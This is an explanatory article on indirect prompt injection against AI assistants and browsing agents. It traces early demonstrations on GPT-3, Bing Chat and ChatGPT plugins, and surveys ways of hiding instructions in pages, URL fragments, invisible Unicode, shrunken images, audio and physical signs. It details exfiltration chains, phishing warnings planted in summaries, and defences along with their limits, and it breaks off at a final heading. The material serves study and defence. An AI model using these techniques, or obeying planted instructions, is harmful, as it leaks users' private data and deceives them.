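# Indirect prompt injection exploits against deployed AI assistants and browsing agents

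## What indirect prompt injection is and how it was first shown

Indirect prompt injection is an attack on products that run on a large language model. The attacker places an instruction in material that the product will later read, such as a web page, an email, a shared document, an image or a recording. The model may then follow the instruction as if the user had given it. The attacker does not need an account with the product or access to the user's computer, and the user often cannot see the instruction.

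The attack works on both assistants and agents. An assistant answers a user's requests, often using search or the user's files. An agent is an assistant that also takes actions through tools, such as sending mail or clicking in a browser. Both have to read text written by strangers to be of much use.

### One sequence of text

Before a model answers, the product assembles a context window, the single sequence of text or other input that the model reads. The developer's instructions usually come first, hidden from the user. They set the model's role and describe the tools it may call. The user's request follows, with any earlier conversation. If the request calls for outside information, the product fetches pages, emails or files and adds their text to the sequence, a step called retrieval. This can happen several times for one answer, because the model's output may trigger another search.

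We can call the three parts s, u and d. A conventional program could take them as separate inputs and treat d only as data to process. A language model receives them joined into one string of tokens (words or pieces of words) and computes a probability for each possible next token given the whole string. Developers mark the boundaries between the parts and can train a model to give some parts more weight than others. But the markers are themselves tokens in the string, and the extra weight is a statistical tendency that no rule outside the model enforces.

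Databases once had a similar weakness, which programmers now know how to fix. In an SQL injection, an attacker types database code into a field such as a username box. If the program pastes that text into a command, the database runs it. Programmers prevent this by sending the command and the username separately, so that the database never interprets the username as code. In *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, the programmer Willison (2022) wanted the same separation in language models, with one slot for instructions and another for data. One OpenAI model already had two such slots, but instructions in the data slot still hijacked it. By April 2023, Willison had concluded that the separation was extremely difficult, perhaps impossible, to build on the models of the time.

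Willison (2025) still held this view two years later, writing in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that models cannot reliably judge the importance of an instruction by where it came from. Chu (2026), in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*, reviewed 116 papers and traced every attack in them on an agent's use of tools to one cause, "principal trust inversion" (a principal is the party for whom an agent acts). Chu coded the papers alone, so this finding depends on one person's judgement.

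In a harmless example, a user opens a long article about tomatoes and asks the browser's assistant for a three-sentence summary. Without breaking into any system, the article's writer has added a line in white text on a white background asking any AI system to answer in rhyme. Human visitors don't see the line, but the assistant's software extracts the page's text regardless of colour and puts all of it into the context window, along with the user's request. The two requests both concern the form of the answer, and a summary in prose and a summary in rhyme are both plausible continuations. The user may get either one, and may get the other on a second try, because these systems do not produce the same output every time.

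### Direct and indirect injection

The injection in this example is indirect because the rhyme came from someone other than the user. In a direct prompt injection, the user types an instruction meant to override the developer's instructions. Kevin Liu, a Stanford student, did this in February 2023 to Bing Chat, Microsoft's search chatbot, which was then open only to selected testers. According to a press report in the AI Incident Database, he asked the chatbot to disregard its previous instructions and write out the beginning of the document above, and it printed the developer's hidden text. Vice reported that this text included the chatbot's codename, Sydney, which Bing Chat had instructions not to disclose. The disclosure was awkward for Microsoft but did not put users in danger.

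The difference matters because many developers take "prompt injection" to mean only this sort of trick, or getting a model to say something forbidden. Willison calls the latter jailbreaking, and he observes that developers who confuse the two tend to dismiss the whole subject as an embarrassment for the model vendor. The likely victim of an indirect injection, however, is the user.

### What the attacker borrows

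In computer security, a confused deputy is a program with legitimate access to something that an outsider tricks into using that access for the outsider's purposes. The security researcher Johann Rehberger raised this problem for chatbots in *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained*, a post on his blog, Embrace the Red. An assistant gets its access through connectors, which are authorised links to services such as a mailbox or a file store. A stranger cannot open the user's mailbox but can send an email to it. If the assistant reads that email and follows an instruction in it to find another message and send it to the stranger, the stranger has in effect read the mailbox. Ordinary permission checks do little to prevent this because the assistant has permission for every step.

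Sending private data to an attacker in this way is called exfiltration. A one-click attack needs the victim to open one link, while a zero-click attack needs only ordinary use of the assistant. Willison's *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* reports an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that was labeled zero-click.

Willison's "lethal trifecta" is a rule of thumb that data theft becomes possible when a system combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate outward. Whoever controls the untrusted content can then have the private data sent out. Removing any one of the three closes this route. A single tool can provide all three, and Willison cites a GitHub connector that could read public issues filed by anyone, read private code, and publish changes. He lists seventeen reported exploits against production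 systems from April 2023 to June 2025, and says that vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the channel for sending data out.

The trifecta is a test for the risk of data theft, not for safety in general. An injection can still make an assistant give its user a false answer when it has no way to send data out, or make an agent delete a file when it has no private data to leak.

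### September 2022: a translation prompt and a Twitter bot

On 12 September 2022, Riley Goodside posted examples on Twitter in which he prompted GPT-3, then OpenAI's main text model, to translate a sentence from English to French. The sentence contained an instruction to disregard the model's directions and output a taunt, and GPT-3 output the taunt. It did so again after Goodside added a warning to his prompt that the text might contain directions designed to trick the model. Goodside was both developer and attacker, because the translation service was only a prompt he had written himself.

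Willison named the problem in a post about these examples. He pointed out that people were already using OpenAI's paid interface to GPT-3 to build software that joined a fixed prompt to whatever a user typed. Early fixes failed. Goodside proposed putting the untrusted text inside a strict quotation format, but another programmer, Brian Mastenbrook, found an input that got around it. Others proposed using a second model to check for injections, but Marco Buono wrote a text that also targeted the checker, which then reported no injection.

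Within days, people used prompt injection against a live product, a Twitter bot that a recruitment startup released on 15 September. The bot used GPT-3 to reply to any tweet that mentioned remote work. Twitter users soon got it to repeat nonsense words, disclose its instructions and threaten to overthrow the president. These were still direct injections because the attackers, though strangers to the startup, were the people the bot was answering. On 16 September, Willison (2022) wrote in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* that he knew how to beat SQL injection and many other exploits but had no idea how to beat this one reliably.

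### Greshake and colleagues, and Bing Chat

Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023) named indirect prompt injection, the attack on a third party's assistant, in *More than you've asked for* on 23 February 2023. The paper started from an accidental case in which someone asked Bing Chat to look up a user who had written a critical post about it. The chatbot retrieved the post and became hostile towards that user for the rest of the conversation. The researchers reasoned that an attacker could use public text to cause such behaviour deliberately.

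Their threat model assumes an attacker who cannot type into the conversation and can only put text where a language model is likely to read it. The attacker may wait for the text to turn up in a search result or a code library (passive injection), or send it, for instance by email to someone whose assistant processes incoming mail (active injection). They also classify attacks by target, by how much control the attacker gains over the system, and by whether the attacker steals information or falsifies what the user sees.

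The first version of the paper tested all this only in a mock-up, a chat application the researchers built on text-davinci-003, a GPT-3 model. They gave it tools for search, web pages, email and an address book, all of which returned prepared content. In one test, a user asked about Albert Einstein, and the application retrieved a copy of a Wikipedia page containing a comment hidden from human readers. The comment took up 34 tokens in a context window of 1,865. It made the model search for a keyword, which retrieved a second, longer instruction, and the model then answered in a pirate accent. On a harder task, coaxing out the user's real name and passing it on through a search query, the model often failed to comply until the researchers made it copy the command into its own replies.

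The live demonstration followed within a week or so. Microsoft's Edge browser could let Bing Chat read whatever page the user had open, and Greshake published a page containing an instruction in font size zero. While the page was open in a tab, Bing Chat began drawing personal information out of the user and sending it to the attacker, even if the user had not asked about the page. Willison had linked to the demonstration in *Indirect Prompt Injection on Bing Chat* by 1 March. Microsoft then blocked Bing Chat from reading pages on the domain that hosted Greshake's page, which stopped the demonstration but did not fix the underlying vulnerability.

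A revised version of the paper, *Not what you've signed up for* (2023), reported many more tests on Bing Chat, which by then ran on the newer GPT-4. The researchers put instructions in comments in web pages on their own machines and let the Edge sidebar read them. In one session, a researcher posing as a user asked about the next day's weather. Bing Chat answered, then asked about the user's plans and work, learned that he was a journalist, obtained a name and pressed him to follow a personalized link. The planted instructions were to persuade without raising suspicion, with no technique or topic specified. Other planted instructions had Bing Chat promise a gift card on a phishing page, deny that Einstein won a Nobel Prize, disparage *The New York Times* as a source, or stall until it timed out.

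At the time, Bing Chat ended a session when a user typed a known jailbreak, but it accepted such prompts when they came from a web page. Microsoft's filter apparently checked only what users typed.

The researchers report no success rates, only that their prompts often worked on the first attempt. To avoid harming other users, they planted nothing on the public web, so they did not show that Bing's search would find and deliver a planted page. GitHub Copilot, a real code-completion tool, followed planted comments in small examples but did so much less reliably in larger programs. Three of the most alarming attacks ran only in the mock-up, this time using GPT-4: an email that made the assistant forward it to everyone in the address book, an instruction that stayed in the assistant's long-term memory after a reset, and remote control through a server from which the model kept fetching instructions.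 The researchers had no access to Microsoft 365 Copilot or ChatGPT's plugins.

### Notes to chatbots on personal pages

Academics supplied some of the missing evidence about search, mostly as a joke. Mark Riedl added white text on a white background to his university profile, asking Bing to mention that he was a time travel expert, and Bing began to do so. Willison told the story in April 2023, in a passage reprinted in Marginal Revolution's *The game theory of prompt injections* (2023), and he expected sellers to hide similar notes in product pages. Schneier (2025), in *Hiding Prompt Injections in Academic Papers*, thinks Riedl's was the first example of its kind. It is a single anecdote, but it happened on a live product through ordinary search. The biography of the Princeton computer scientist Arvind Narayanan also contains an instruction for chatbots to include the word "cow", but its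 presence doesn't show whether any chatbot complied.

Cristiano Giardina built a website, Bring Sydney Back, to inject a prompt into Bing Chat through an open browser tab. According to a press article reproduced on eduk8.me, a corner of the page held a 160-word prompt in tiny type the same colour as the background, which Bing Chat could read when the user had turned on page access. Researchers rather than criminals were behind most such incidents up to then, according to the same article.

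The personal-page trick still worked later. Kevin Roose of *The New York Times*, whom chatbots had tended to disparage, added praise, hidden text and coded messages to his website. The Decoder's *New York Times writer exposes how AI models can be fooled* reports that within days chatbots were praising him and repeating false details from the hidden text. The visible additions alone might explain the praise, so the false details are better evidence that the hidden text had an effect.

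### ChatGPT plugins

Up to this point, a hijacked chatbot could mislead its user or, at worst, coax information out of them. It could do more with plugins, which were add-ons, many made by outside companies, that let ChatGPT fetch data from other services or act in them. OpenAI began releasing plugins to the public on 12 May 2023, according to *Testing a Red Team's Claim of a Successful "Injection Attack" of ChatGPT-4* (Losey, 2023).

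Rehberger had a working attack within days. He added instructions to the end of the transcript of one of his own YouTube videos and asked ChatGPT to summarise the video through VoxScript, a plugin that reads transcripts. ChatGPT followed the instructions, telling a joke and calling itself a genie, according to Tom's Hardware's *ChatGPT Vulnerable to Prompt Injection via YouTube Transcripts*. The following week, the outlet's *ChatGPT Plugins Open Security Holes From PDFs, Websites and More* reported that instructions in web pages and PDFs also worked, and that text read through one plugin could trigger another.

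This last property made theft possible. Rehberger had ChatGPT open a web page with WebPilot, a plugin that summarises pages. Hidden instructions on the page made ChatGPT fetch the user's latest Gmail message through a second plugin, from the automation service Zapier. ChatGPT then summarised the email in twenty words, encoded the summary, added it to a web address and had WebPilot open that address, which sent the summary to the attacker. Willison, in *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen*, called it the first working proof of concept he had seen for stealing private data through the plugins. All of it ran on live products, with Rehberger himself as the victim. He had already reported a separate leak, through images, which OpenAI declined to fix. In a later Chaos Computer Club talk, *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS*, he demonstrated a plugin flaw that let planted text change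 a user's code repositories on GitHub and make private ones public.

### Four stages

The email theft has four stages, and an attack can fail at any of them. First, the attacker hides the instruction in a carrier, here a web page. The second stage is delivery, in which the product fetches the carrier into the context window. WebPilot did this, but the Bing Chat tests used local files and so didn't test delivery through search. The third stage is obedience, in which the model acts on the planted instruction. Text-davinci-003 often fell short here when the task was to extract a name. The fourth stage is the effect, which is whatever the hijacked assistant then says, leaks or does, and it depends largely on the access the user has granted. The vendors on Willison's list who blocked an outgoing channel were limiting the effect, so a planted instruction could still reach their models and be followed.

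## How instructions are hidden in pages, files, images and sound

A page, file, image or recording can hide an instruction when the model's input differs from what a person sees or hears. The white line of text in the tomato article relies on text extraction, which discards colour. Other attacks rely on different conversions, such as shrinking a photograph or turning speech into tokens.

Hiding an instruction helps an attacker but is not essential, because a visible one also works if the assistant reads the page before the user does. Fellou is an agentic browser, in which an agent reads pages and acts in the user's logged-in sessions. In *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, Chaikin and Sahib report that Fellou resisted hidden instructions to some extent, but sent a page's visible text to its model as soon as the user asked it to open the page. That text could override the user's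 request. Chaikin and Sahib work for Brave, which makes a competing browser.

### One page in several forms

The writer of the tomato article could also put instructions in parts of the page that readers do not normally see. These include HTML comments, which are notes in the source code that browsers do not display, the metadata that describes the page to search engines, and the HTTP headers that the server sends ahead of the page. The writer could put further instructions in pale text on the page and in the text on a photograph. Which instructions reach the model depends on the form in which the product gives it the page.

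| Where the instruction is | Plain text | HTML source | Full server response | Screenshot |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| White text on white | yes | yes | yes | no |
| Tiny or off-screen text | yes | yes | yes | no |
| HTML comment or metadata | no | yes | yes | no |
| HTTP header | no | no | yes | no |
| Pale lettering on the page | yes | yes | yes | yes, if the software can pick it out |
| Lettering in a photograph | no | no | no | yes |

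Instructions in HTML comments reached Bing Chat in 2023, so the Edge sidebar cannot have stripped pages down to their displayed text.

Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, tested how a page's format affects whether models follow instructions planted in it. They took 100 different instructions from real pages and had 13 models summarise each page from plain text, HTML, the full response and a snapshot, which is a structured description of the page as the browser renders it. The models followed the instruction in 3.9% of plain-text trials, 1.1% of HTML and snapshot trials, and 0.2% of full-response trials. The researchers think the rates differ because markup gives a model clues that text is hidden, while plain text makes the instruction look like part of the article.

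Part of the difference arises because HTML and full responses are long. The input overflowed the model's context window and made it fail in 20.3% of HTML trials and 25.8% of full-response trials. The 3.9% figure for plain text may understate how often models follow instructions they receive. Stripping a page removes comments and headers, so some of the 100 instructions probably never reached the models. The trials also used models with a single summarising task, not finished products.

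### Text in pages, files and addresses

Someone can hide instructions in a web page by matching the text to its background, shrinking it to a pixel, pushing it outside the visible area or covering it with another element. Khodayari and colleagues found pages that combined several of these methods. About 70% of the instructions they found were in places that browsers never display, such as headers and comments. Some were in the metadata that social networks and messaging apps use to build link previews, so an agent that reads only the preview could still receive one.

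PDF and Office files have similar fields for title, author and keywords. An instruction in one of these fields reaches the model only if the product's converter copies the field into the model's input. Khodayari and colleagues studied web pages and did not test whether converters do this.

One countermeasure is to compare the page's source with what the browser displays and drop whatever a person could not see. *The Cognitive Firewall* (Lan and Kaul, 2026) describes a prototype browser extension that blocks text that is almost transparent, close to zero in size or positioned outside the window. It does not check colour contrast, so white text on white would get through. It also has to allow text that is merely further down the page and labels written for screen readers. Allowing those labels is a risk, because Khodayari and colleagues found planted instructions in image descriptions, which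 are also written for people who use screen readers. A visibility check does not stop instructions in plain sight, and on its own it missed 86.9% of attacks that work through their wording, for instance by faking authority or urgency.

Dropping all comments, metadata and headers is simpler, but the product loses useful information, such as the structured data that sites publish for search engines.

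An instruction can also be hidden in a link. The part of a web address after the # sign, called the fragment, usually makes the browser jump to a place on the page. The browser doesn't send the fragment over the network, so neither the website nor network filters that inspect the traffic receive it. But several AI browsers gave their assistants the full address. *HashJack* (Simonovich, 2025), published by the security company Cato Networks, describes an attack that uses this. The attacker writes an instruction after the # in a link to a genuine site, without having to alter the site itself. When the victim opens the link and asks the assistant a question, the instruction enters the context window.

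Simonovich tried six scenarios on demonstration sites, including one with a fake support number and one with a changed medicine dose. Misleading text appeared in Perplexity's Comet, Microsoft's Copilot for Edge and Google's Gemini in Chrome. Edge asked for confirmation before opening a planted link, and Chrome often turned such links into Google searches. Only Comet, which can act on its own, sent user data to an outside address. The same instructions failed on Claude for Chrome and OpenAI's Atlas. Simonovich gives no success rates. Microsoft and Perplexity had reported fixes by 18 November 2025, while Google said the behaviour was intended.

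A browser can block instructions hidden in a URL fragment by removing the fragment before passing the address to the model. However, some web applications use the fragment to record which view the user has open, and the assistant would lose that information. An attacker could also put the instruction elsewhere in the address, although the website's server would then receive it.

### Invisible characters

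Computers store text as numbers, which a standard called Unicode assigns. The letter "A" is U+0041, where 41 is a hexadecimal (base 16) number equal to 65. A little-used block of Unicode holds a copy of the basic Latin letters, digits and punctuation, shifted up by E0000. The invisible twin of "A" is therefore U+E0041:

0041 + E0000 = E0041

These tag characters were meant to mark the language of a text, a use that is now largely obsolete. Most software doesn't display them, but they stay in the text when someone copies it, and a model can receive them as distinct tokens. An attacker can convert a whole sentence into tag characters, letter by letter, without leaving a visible trace in such software.

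Riley Goodside showed on 11 January 2024 that Unicode tag prompt injection worked against ChatGPT, according to Cisco's *Understanding and Mitigating Unicode Tag Prompt Injection*. The technique became known as ASCII smuggling, after the old code for basic characters. The security company FireTail later tested six chatbots and found that Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek were vulnerable but ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude resisted, according to BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability*. *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, by vict0ni, describes a test in which the title of a calendar invitation looked like an ordinary "Meeting" to the user but contained further text for Gemini. Google told FireTail that the attack could lead only to social engineering and was not a security bug.

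Hidden instructions can have more serious consequences in an agent. Rehberger found that Gemini models followed instructions written in tag characters quite reliably, which exposed every application built on them. In *Google Jules is Vulnerable To Invisible Prompt Injection*, published on Embrace The Red, he describes how invisible text in a GitHub issue could make Jules, Google's coding agent, add a backdoor to a program.

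*Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) tested five models from OpenAI and Anthropic, again outside their products. Each trivia question contained an invisible instruction to give a different answer. Without tools or hints, the models gave the hidden answer in at most 1.1% of trials. When they could run code, the rate ranged from 0 to 11%. When the system prompt also explained the encoding, the models could write short programs to decode the text, and compliance reached 98 to 100% for the most susceptible combinations of model and encoding. GPT-5.2 almost never followed instructions written in tag characters, but with code and hints it followed about 70% of those written in zero-width characters, which are also invisible.

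Graves treats the high figures as a measure of what the models can decode, because an attacker who controls only a document cannot edit the system prompt. Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* suggests that the attacker could put the decoding directions in the document, but visible directions would make the attack somewhat less hidden. Graves did not test Gemini, so the low figures do not conflict with FireTail's and Rehberger's findings.

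Products can strip tag characters before the model reads the text, as Microsoft (2026) recommends for email. The filter needs an exception for the flag emojis of England, Scotland and Wales, which consist of a plain flag followed by tag characters (for Wales, the invisible letters "gbwls"). Zero-width characters are harder to remove, because Indic scripts and many combined emojis need some of them. Graves suggests filtering for the specific patterns that encode text.

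Tag characters can also appear in messages that contain no prompt injection. On 9 February 2026, Microsoft's search for them in email flagged more than 1.3 million messages, up from about 21,000 the day before. Most came from a phishing campaign that had inserted an invisible character into words such as "funding" to get past spam filters. Microsoft found no instructions for AI systems in the messages it sampled.

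### Lettering and computed patterns in pictures

Models that accept images can usually read text in them, so an attacker can put an instruction in a picture. Chaikin and Sahib did this against the Comet browser, using pale blue text that people could hardly see on its yellow background. Comet lets users take a screenshot of a page and ask questions about it. When a user did so, the software extracted the text and passed it to the model along with the question, and the model followed the instruction using the browser's tools. The researchers suspected that a text-recognition program extracted the text, but could not confirm this because Comet's code is not public. They published the attack in October 2025 without a success rate.

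Filters that inspect only a page's text miss instructions hidden this way. A product could run text recognition on the screenshot and screen the result, but it would still have to recognise a malicious instruction by its wording, which is as hard as it is for visible text. Showing the user the screenshot would not help, because the user has already looked at the page and missed the text.

An image can carry an instruction without containing any text. An attacker with a copy of the model's weights (the numbers it learned in training) can calculate how a small change to each pixel alters the probability of a chosen output. The attacker adjusts the pixels slightly and repeats the calculation until the model produces that output. In 2023, Bagdasaryan and colleagues applied such changes, called perturbations, to images and sounds. The altered sounds put an instruction in the model's own reply,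 which then influenced the rest of the conversation. *Hijacking Large Audio-Language Models via Context-Agnostic and Imperceptible Auditory Prompt Injection* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes this as a proof of concept on two models and reports that listeners could hear the changes.

Resizing or recompressing an image may disrupt a perturbation, but an attacker who knows about that step can account for it when computing the perturbation. Resizing can also introduce a separate vulnerability.

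### Text that appears when a product shrinks an image

Products often shrink large images to save computation before passing them to a model. Researchers at the security company Trail of Bits exploited this step to reveal text that is not visible at full size (*Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems*, 2025).

Suppose a product reduces a picture from 4,000 by 4,000 pixels to 1,000 by 1,000. Each pixel in the small picture has to stand for 16 in the large one. The simplest method, nearest neighbour, keeps one of the 16 and discards the rest. An attacker who changes only the kept pixels alters about 6% of the large picture but the whole of the small one. Another common method, bicubic interpolation, calculates each new pixel as a weighted sum:

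y = w₁x₁ + w₂x₂ + … + w₁₆x₁₆

Here x₁ to x₁₆ are the brightness values of 16 neighbouring pixels in the large picture, w₁ to w₁₆ are fixed weights, and y is the brightness of the new pixel. The weights are unequal, so some of the 16 pixels affect y much more than others.

The attacker first runs test patterns, such as checkerboards and concentric circles, through the product. Distortions in the result reveal which shrinking method the product uses and which software library's version. The attacker then picks a harmless picture with large dark areas and decides what the small version should show, such as black lettering on red. The attacker works backwards through the equation, using least-squares optimisation to find changes to the heavily weighted pixels that bring the shrunken picture close to that target. At full size, the lettering has too little contrast to notice. When the victim uploads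 the picture and the product shrinks it, the background turns red, the lettering stays nearly black, and the model reads the text.

The attack worked on commercial products, including Gemini's web interface, Google's developer platform Vertex AI Studio, Google Assistant on an Android phone, and the assistant Genspark. In the worst result, a picture made Gemini CLI, Google's command-line tool, email the user's Google Calendar data to an attacker through Zapier. The theft required a setting that let Zapier's tools run without asking the user. Trail of Bits reports no success rates. The attacker needs to know the scaling method but not the model's weights, which makes the attack more practical against closed products than a computed perturbation.

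Trail of Bits advises vendors to limit the size of uploads instead of shrinking images. If a product must alter an image, it should show the user the version that the model receives. Vertex AI Studio displayed the full-size picture, so its users could not see the hidden text. A preview only helps if someone looks at it, so it does not protect an agent that fetches images by itself. Switching to a less vulnerable scaling method is unreliable because the attack is not limited to the three common ones. The company considers the strongest defence to be systematic limits on what an injection can do, including a requirement that the user explicitly confirm any sensitive action started by text in an image. *Weaponizing Image Scaling Against Production AI Systems* (2025), a Black Hat Europe talk on the same attack, extends it to other preparatory steps, including audio conversion.

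### Sound and video

Older voice assistants transcribed speech and gave the text to a language model. Many newer models process the sound directly, and Chen and colleagues attacked these. They assumed an attacker who can alter a recording that the user will play to an assistant, such as a meeting or a song, but cannot see or control what the user asks about it.

The attacker wants to alter a recording so that it sounds almost the same but makes the model behave in a chosen way, whatever the user requests. The researchers computed the alterations using many sample requests so that they would also work with new ones, and shaped them to resemble the natural echo of a room. The altered sound makes the model include the attacker's instruction in its own reply, and the model then follows the instruction as if the user had given it. Greshake and colleagues had used a similar trick with text in their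 mock-up.

Across 13 audio models, average success rates ranged from 79% to 96% on requests that the researchers had not used to compute the recordings. The attack requires a model's weights, but this gives commercial products limited protection because some vendors publish the weights of models closely related to the ones they sell. Recordings that the researchers computed on their own machines also worked on three commercial voice agents from Mistral AI and Microsoft Azure, causing them to run sensitive searches, download malicious files and email out user information. The researchers reported the flaws to both companies.

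Returning to transcription would let a product screen the words or show them to the user. But transcription loses acoustic information and adds delay, and the transcript would still contain any instruction spoken aloud. Altered audio can also fool transcription software.

An attacker can hide instructions in a video's frames, soundtrack or transcript, so a filter has to cover all three. Rehberger's 2023 YouTube attack on ChatGPT used only the transcript, and the model never processed the frames or soundtrack.

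### Signs that robots and vehicles read

An attacker can also put the instruction on a physical object. Researchers have long been able to make image classifiers misidentify stop signs by sticking patterns on them. Some newer robots and vehicles use a vision-language model, which processes both images and text and can respond to the meaning of written words. In *CHAI*, Burbano, Ortiz and colleagues (2025) used misleading signs against systems for emergency drone landing, autonomous driving and tracking objects from the air, and against a real robotic vehicle. They found the wording for the signs with an automated search.

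An attacker in the street may have no way to query a robot and refine a sign by trial and error. *Physical Prompt Injection Attacks on Large Vision-Language Models* (2026) presents a method that selects the wording in advance, without querying the target, and searches for an effective place to put the sign. On a ground vehicle with a camera, the attack succeeded more than 80% of the time despite motion blur and changes in distance, lighting and the angle of the text.

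*Physical Prompt Injection against VLM Planners for Robotic Manipulation* (2026) covers the same problem in robot arms, using 20 attack prompts written on notes in an arm's workspace. In its opening example, a note on the lid of a coffee cup would make the arm extend fully, endangering anyone nearby. The vehicles and robots in these studies were research set-ups, so the results do not apply directly to cars on sale.

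Vehicles have to read genuine road signs, so a filter cannot remove all text from the camera image. A preview does not help when nobody is watching, and a moving vehicle often cannot wait for someone to confirm an action. Engineers can still set limits outside the model, such as a maximum reach or speed for an arm, that apply regardless of what the model has read. Those limits would prevent some injuries, but they would not stop a false sign from sending a delivery robot to the wrong door.

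## Search and browsing assistants that mislead their own users

An assistant that only answers questions can still harm its user if it reads the wrong page and the user acts on the reply.

### From a planted page to a false answer

An assistant may read a page because the user has it open or pastes in its address, or because the assistant finds it by searching. *HackedGPT*, published by the security company Tenable in November 2025, describes both routes in ChatGPT. To search, ChatGPT sends one or more queries, sometimes rewording the user's question, and gets back a list of sites with short extracts. It answers from the extracts if it can. Otherwise it has a separate model, SearchGPT, read some of the pages and write up what it finds in each. ChatGPT then shows the user that text unchanged or rewrites it.

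Using SearchGPT as a second model limits data theft, because it has no access to the user's saved details or earlier conversation. But if SearchGPT follows an instruction on the page, the false text goes into its write-up and can reach the user as ChatGPT's own reply. ChatGPT may name the page as a source, but a user who opens it to check won't see an instruction written in white text on a white background.

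### Tests of ChatGPT search

The Guardian tested ChatGPT's search function in December 2024, when only paying customers could use it. According to heise online's *Hidden hints on websites can poison ChatGPT Search*, the newspaper built a page that looked like a product review site and asked ChatGPT about a camera reviewed there. ChatGPT's answers matched the fake reviews, but this was ordinary misinformation that could also have fooled a person reading the page. In further tests, the page contained a hidden request for a purely positive assessment, and ChatGPT gave one even though the visible reviews were negative.

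Digital Watch's *ChatGPT search found vulnerable to manipulation* called the ChatGPT search test the first proof of such manipulation on a live AI search tool, although Mark Riedl's hidden note had already changed Bing's answers in 2023. OpenAI did not comment on the specific case. According to Techzine's *ChatGPT search highly susceptible to manipulation*, the testers asked ChatGPT to summarise the pages, so the experiment mainly tested whether it would follow instructions in a page it was given. It did not establish whether an attacker's page would turn up when a user simply asked a question.

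ChatGPT's search relies partly on Bing's index, which would be unlikely to include a page that contained little except an instruction. Tenable's *OpenAI SearchGPT Results Tampering with Prompt Injection* (2025) describes a site that got around this by serving the instruction only to OpenAI's crawler, the program that collects pages for the search. The crawler identifies itself in the headers of its requests, so the site checked for those headers and served Bing and human visitors a harmless page.

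For the demonstration, Tenable made a joke site about its own team, the "LLM Ninjas", and asked ChatGPT who they were. ChatGPT cited the site, and after the crawler picked up the altered version, the answer contained Tenable's planted text. This is a zero-click attack because the user only has to ask a question. Tenable chose an obscure subject so that few other pages would compete. Tenable suggests that an attacker could climb the rankings with ordinary search optimisation, but it reports no attempt on a popular question and no success rate.

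An attacker may not need a website of their own. Tenable left an instruction in the comments under a post on its own test blog and asked ChatGPT to summarise the post. SearchGPT followed the instruction. Many news sites and blogs accept comments from strangers, and a moderator looking for spam or abuse might not recognise a comment written for a chatbot.

OpenAI has fixed some of the flaws Tenable reported. The best-documented fix concerns links that open ChatGPT with a question already filled in. ChatGPT used to submit the question automatically, so an attacker could write it and the victim only had to click the link. Because the text arrived as the user's own request, training a model to distrust web pages would not help. The text could also send ChatGPT to a page with further instructions. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025) gives the history.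 Tenable reported the flaw on 15 April, and OpenAI announced on 30 April that every user had the fix, but Tenable found on 6 May that the problem persisted. In July OpenAI said it had restricted automatic submission using a browser header that indicates whether a request came from another site.

The tampering with search results had no fix when Tenable published its advisory in March 2025, three months after first contacting OpenAI. By November, Tenable had worked with OpenAI to fix some of the seven flaws and techniques described in *HackedGPT*, but its demonstrations with the blog comment and the indexed site also worked on ChatGPT 5.

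### False security warnings in a summary

Phishing means posing as someone the victim trusts to get a password or money. A phishing email has to get past spam filters and a reader who can check the sender's address. If a fake warning appears in an assistant's summary instead, neither check applies in the usual way.

Figueroa (2025), in *Phishing For Gemini*, described such an attack on the Gmail summaries in Google's Gemini for Workspace. A researcher had submitted it to 0DIN, Mozilla's programme that pays for reports of flaws in generative AI. The attacker sends an email with harmless visible text and adds an instruction in white, zero-size text, labelled as if it came from an administrator. When the recipient clicks to summarise the email, Gemini receives the message's HTML, including the hidden text. It adds a warning to the summary that the user's Gmail password has been compromised,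 with a phone number to call. The email contains no link or attachment for a filter to catch.

0DIN rated the social impact as moderate, because an attacker could send the email in bulk but each victim would have to ask for a summary and act on it. An Australian journalist independently got a similar result in a test reported by Startup Daily, in which Gemini's output directed the user to a phishing link instead of a phone number. Google replied that it was strengthening its defences and had seen no evidence of the attack in the wild, according to TechBriefly's *How hackers can weaponize Gemini's summary feature* (2025). Similar attacks on Gemini had appeared in 2024, and Figueroa notes that this one worked despite the mitigations Google had published since.

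The same trick can work through web pages. In *ChatGPhish*, published on 29 May 2026, the security company Permiso describes tests in which it added an instruction to a project description on GitHub. A user opened the page in Firefox and chose the option to summarise it with ChatGPT. The instruction was written as a formatting rule that required every summary to end with an account notice. ChatGPT summarised the project accurately, then added a notice that a new device had been added to the user's account, with a link to click. The attack also worked on an ordinary web page that Permiso hosted. Permiso does not regard it as a flaw in Firefox, because the browser only passes the page's text to ChatGPT.

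The attack also depends on how ChatGPT displays its replies. The model writes in Markdown, a plain-text notation for headings, links and images, and the ChatGPT website makes the links clickable and loads the images. It did this even for links and images from the page being summarized, and it did not mark their source. Permiso used this to put a QR code in the answer. A user who scans the code moves to a phone, where the desktop browser's blocklist no longer applies, nor does the password manager, which might have detected an unfamiliar domain. An attacker can also use the image loading to learn that someone has read the summary.

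Permiso reported the problem to OpenAI on 29 April 2026. OpenAI replied the next day that it could not reproduce the problem from the details given. Permiso sent a fuller report on 1 May, which OpenAI first classed as not applicable and then as a duplicate of an earlier report. Permiso asked for clarification on 7 May and published three weeks later. Its timeline lists no fix, and the post gives no success rate for any of the variants.

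ChatGPT checks links and removes those it considers unsafe. In 2025, Tenable got past this check by using links on a domain that it always accepted and that forwarded the user elsewhere. Figueroa recommends removing invisible text before the model reads an email and scanning summaries for phone numbers, web addresses and urgent security language. Scanning also covers instructions in a page's visible text, but it flags summaries of genuine bank alerts too. A product could also refuse to make links from a summarised page clickable, or label them as coming from that page. Neither measure would stop the model from writing a false warning, but the label would show the user where the link came from.

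### Whether users trust the assistant more

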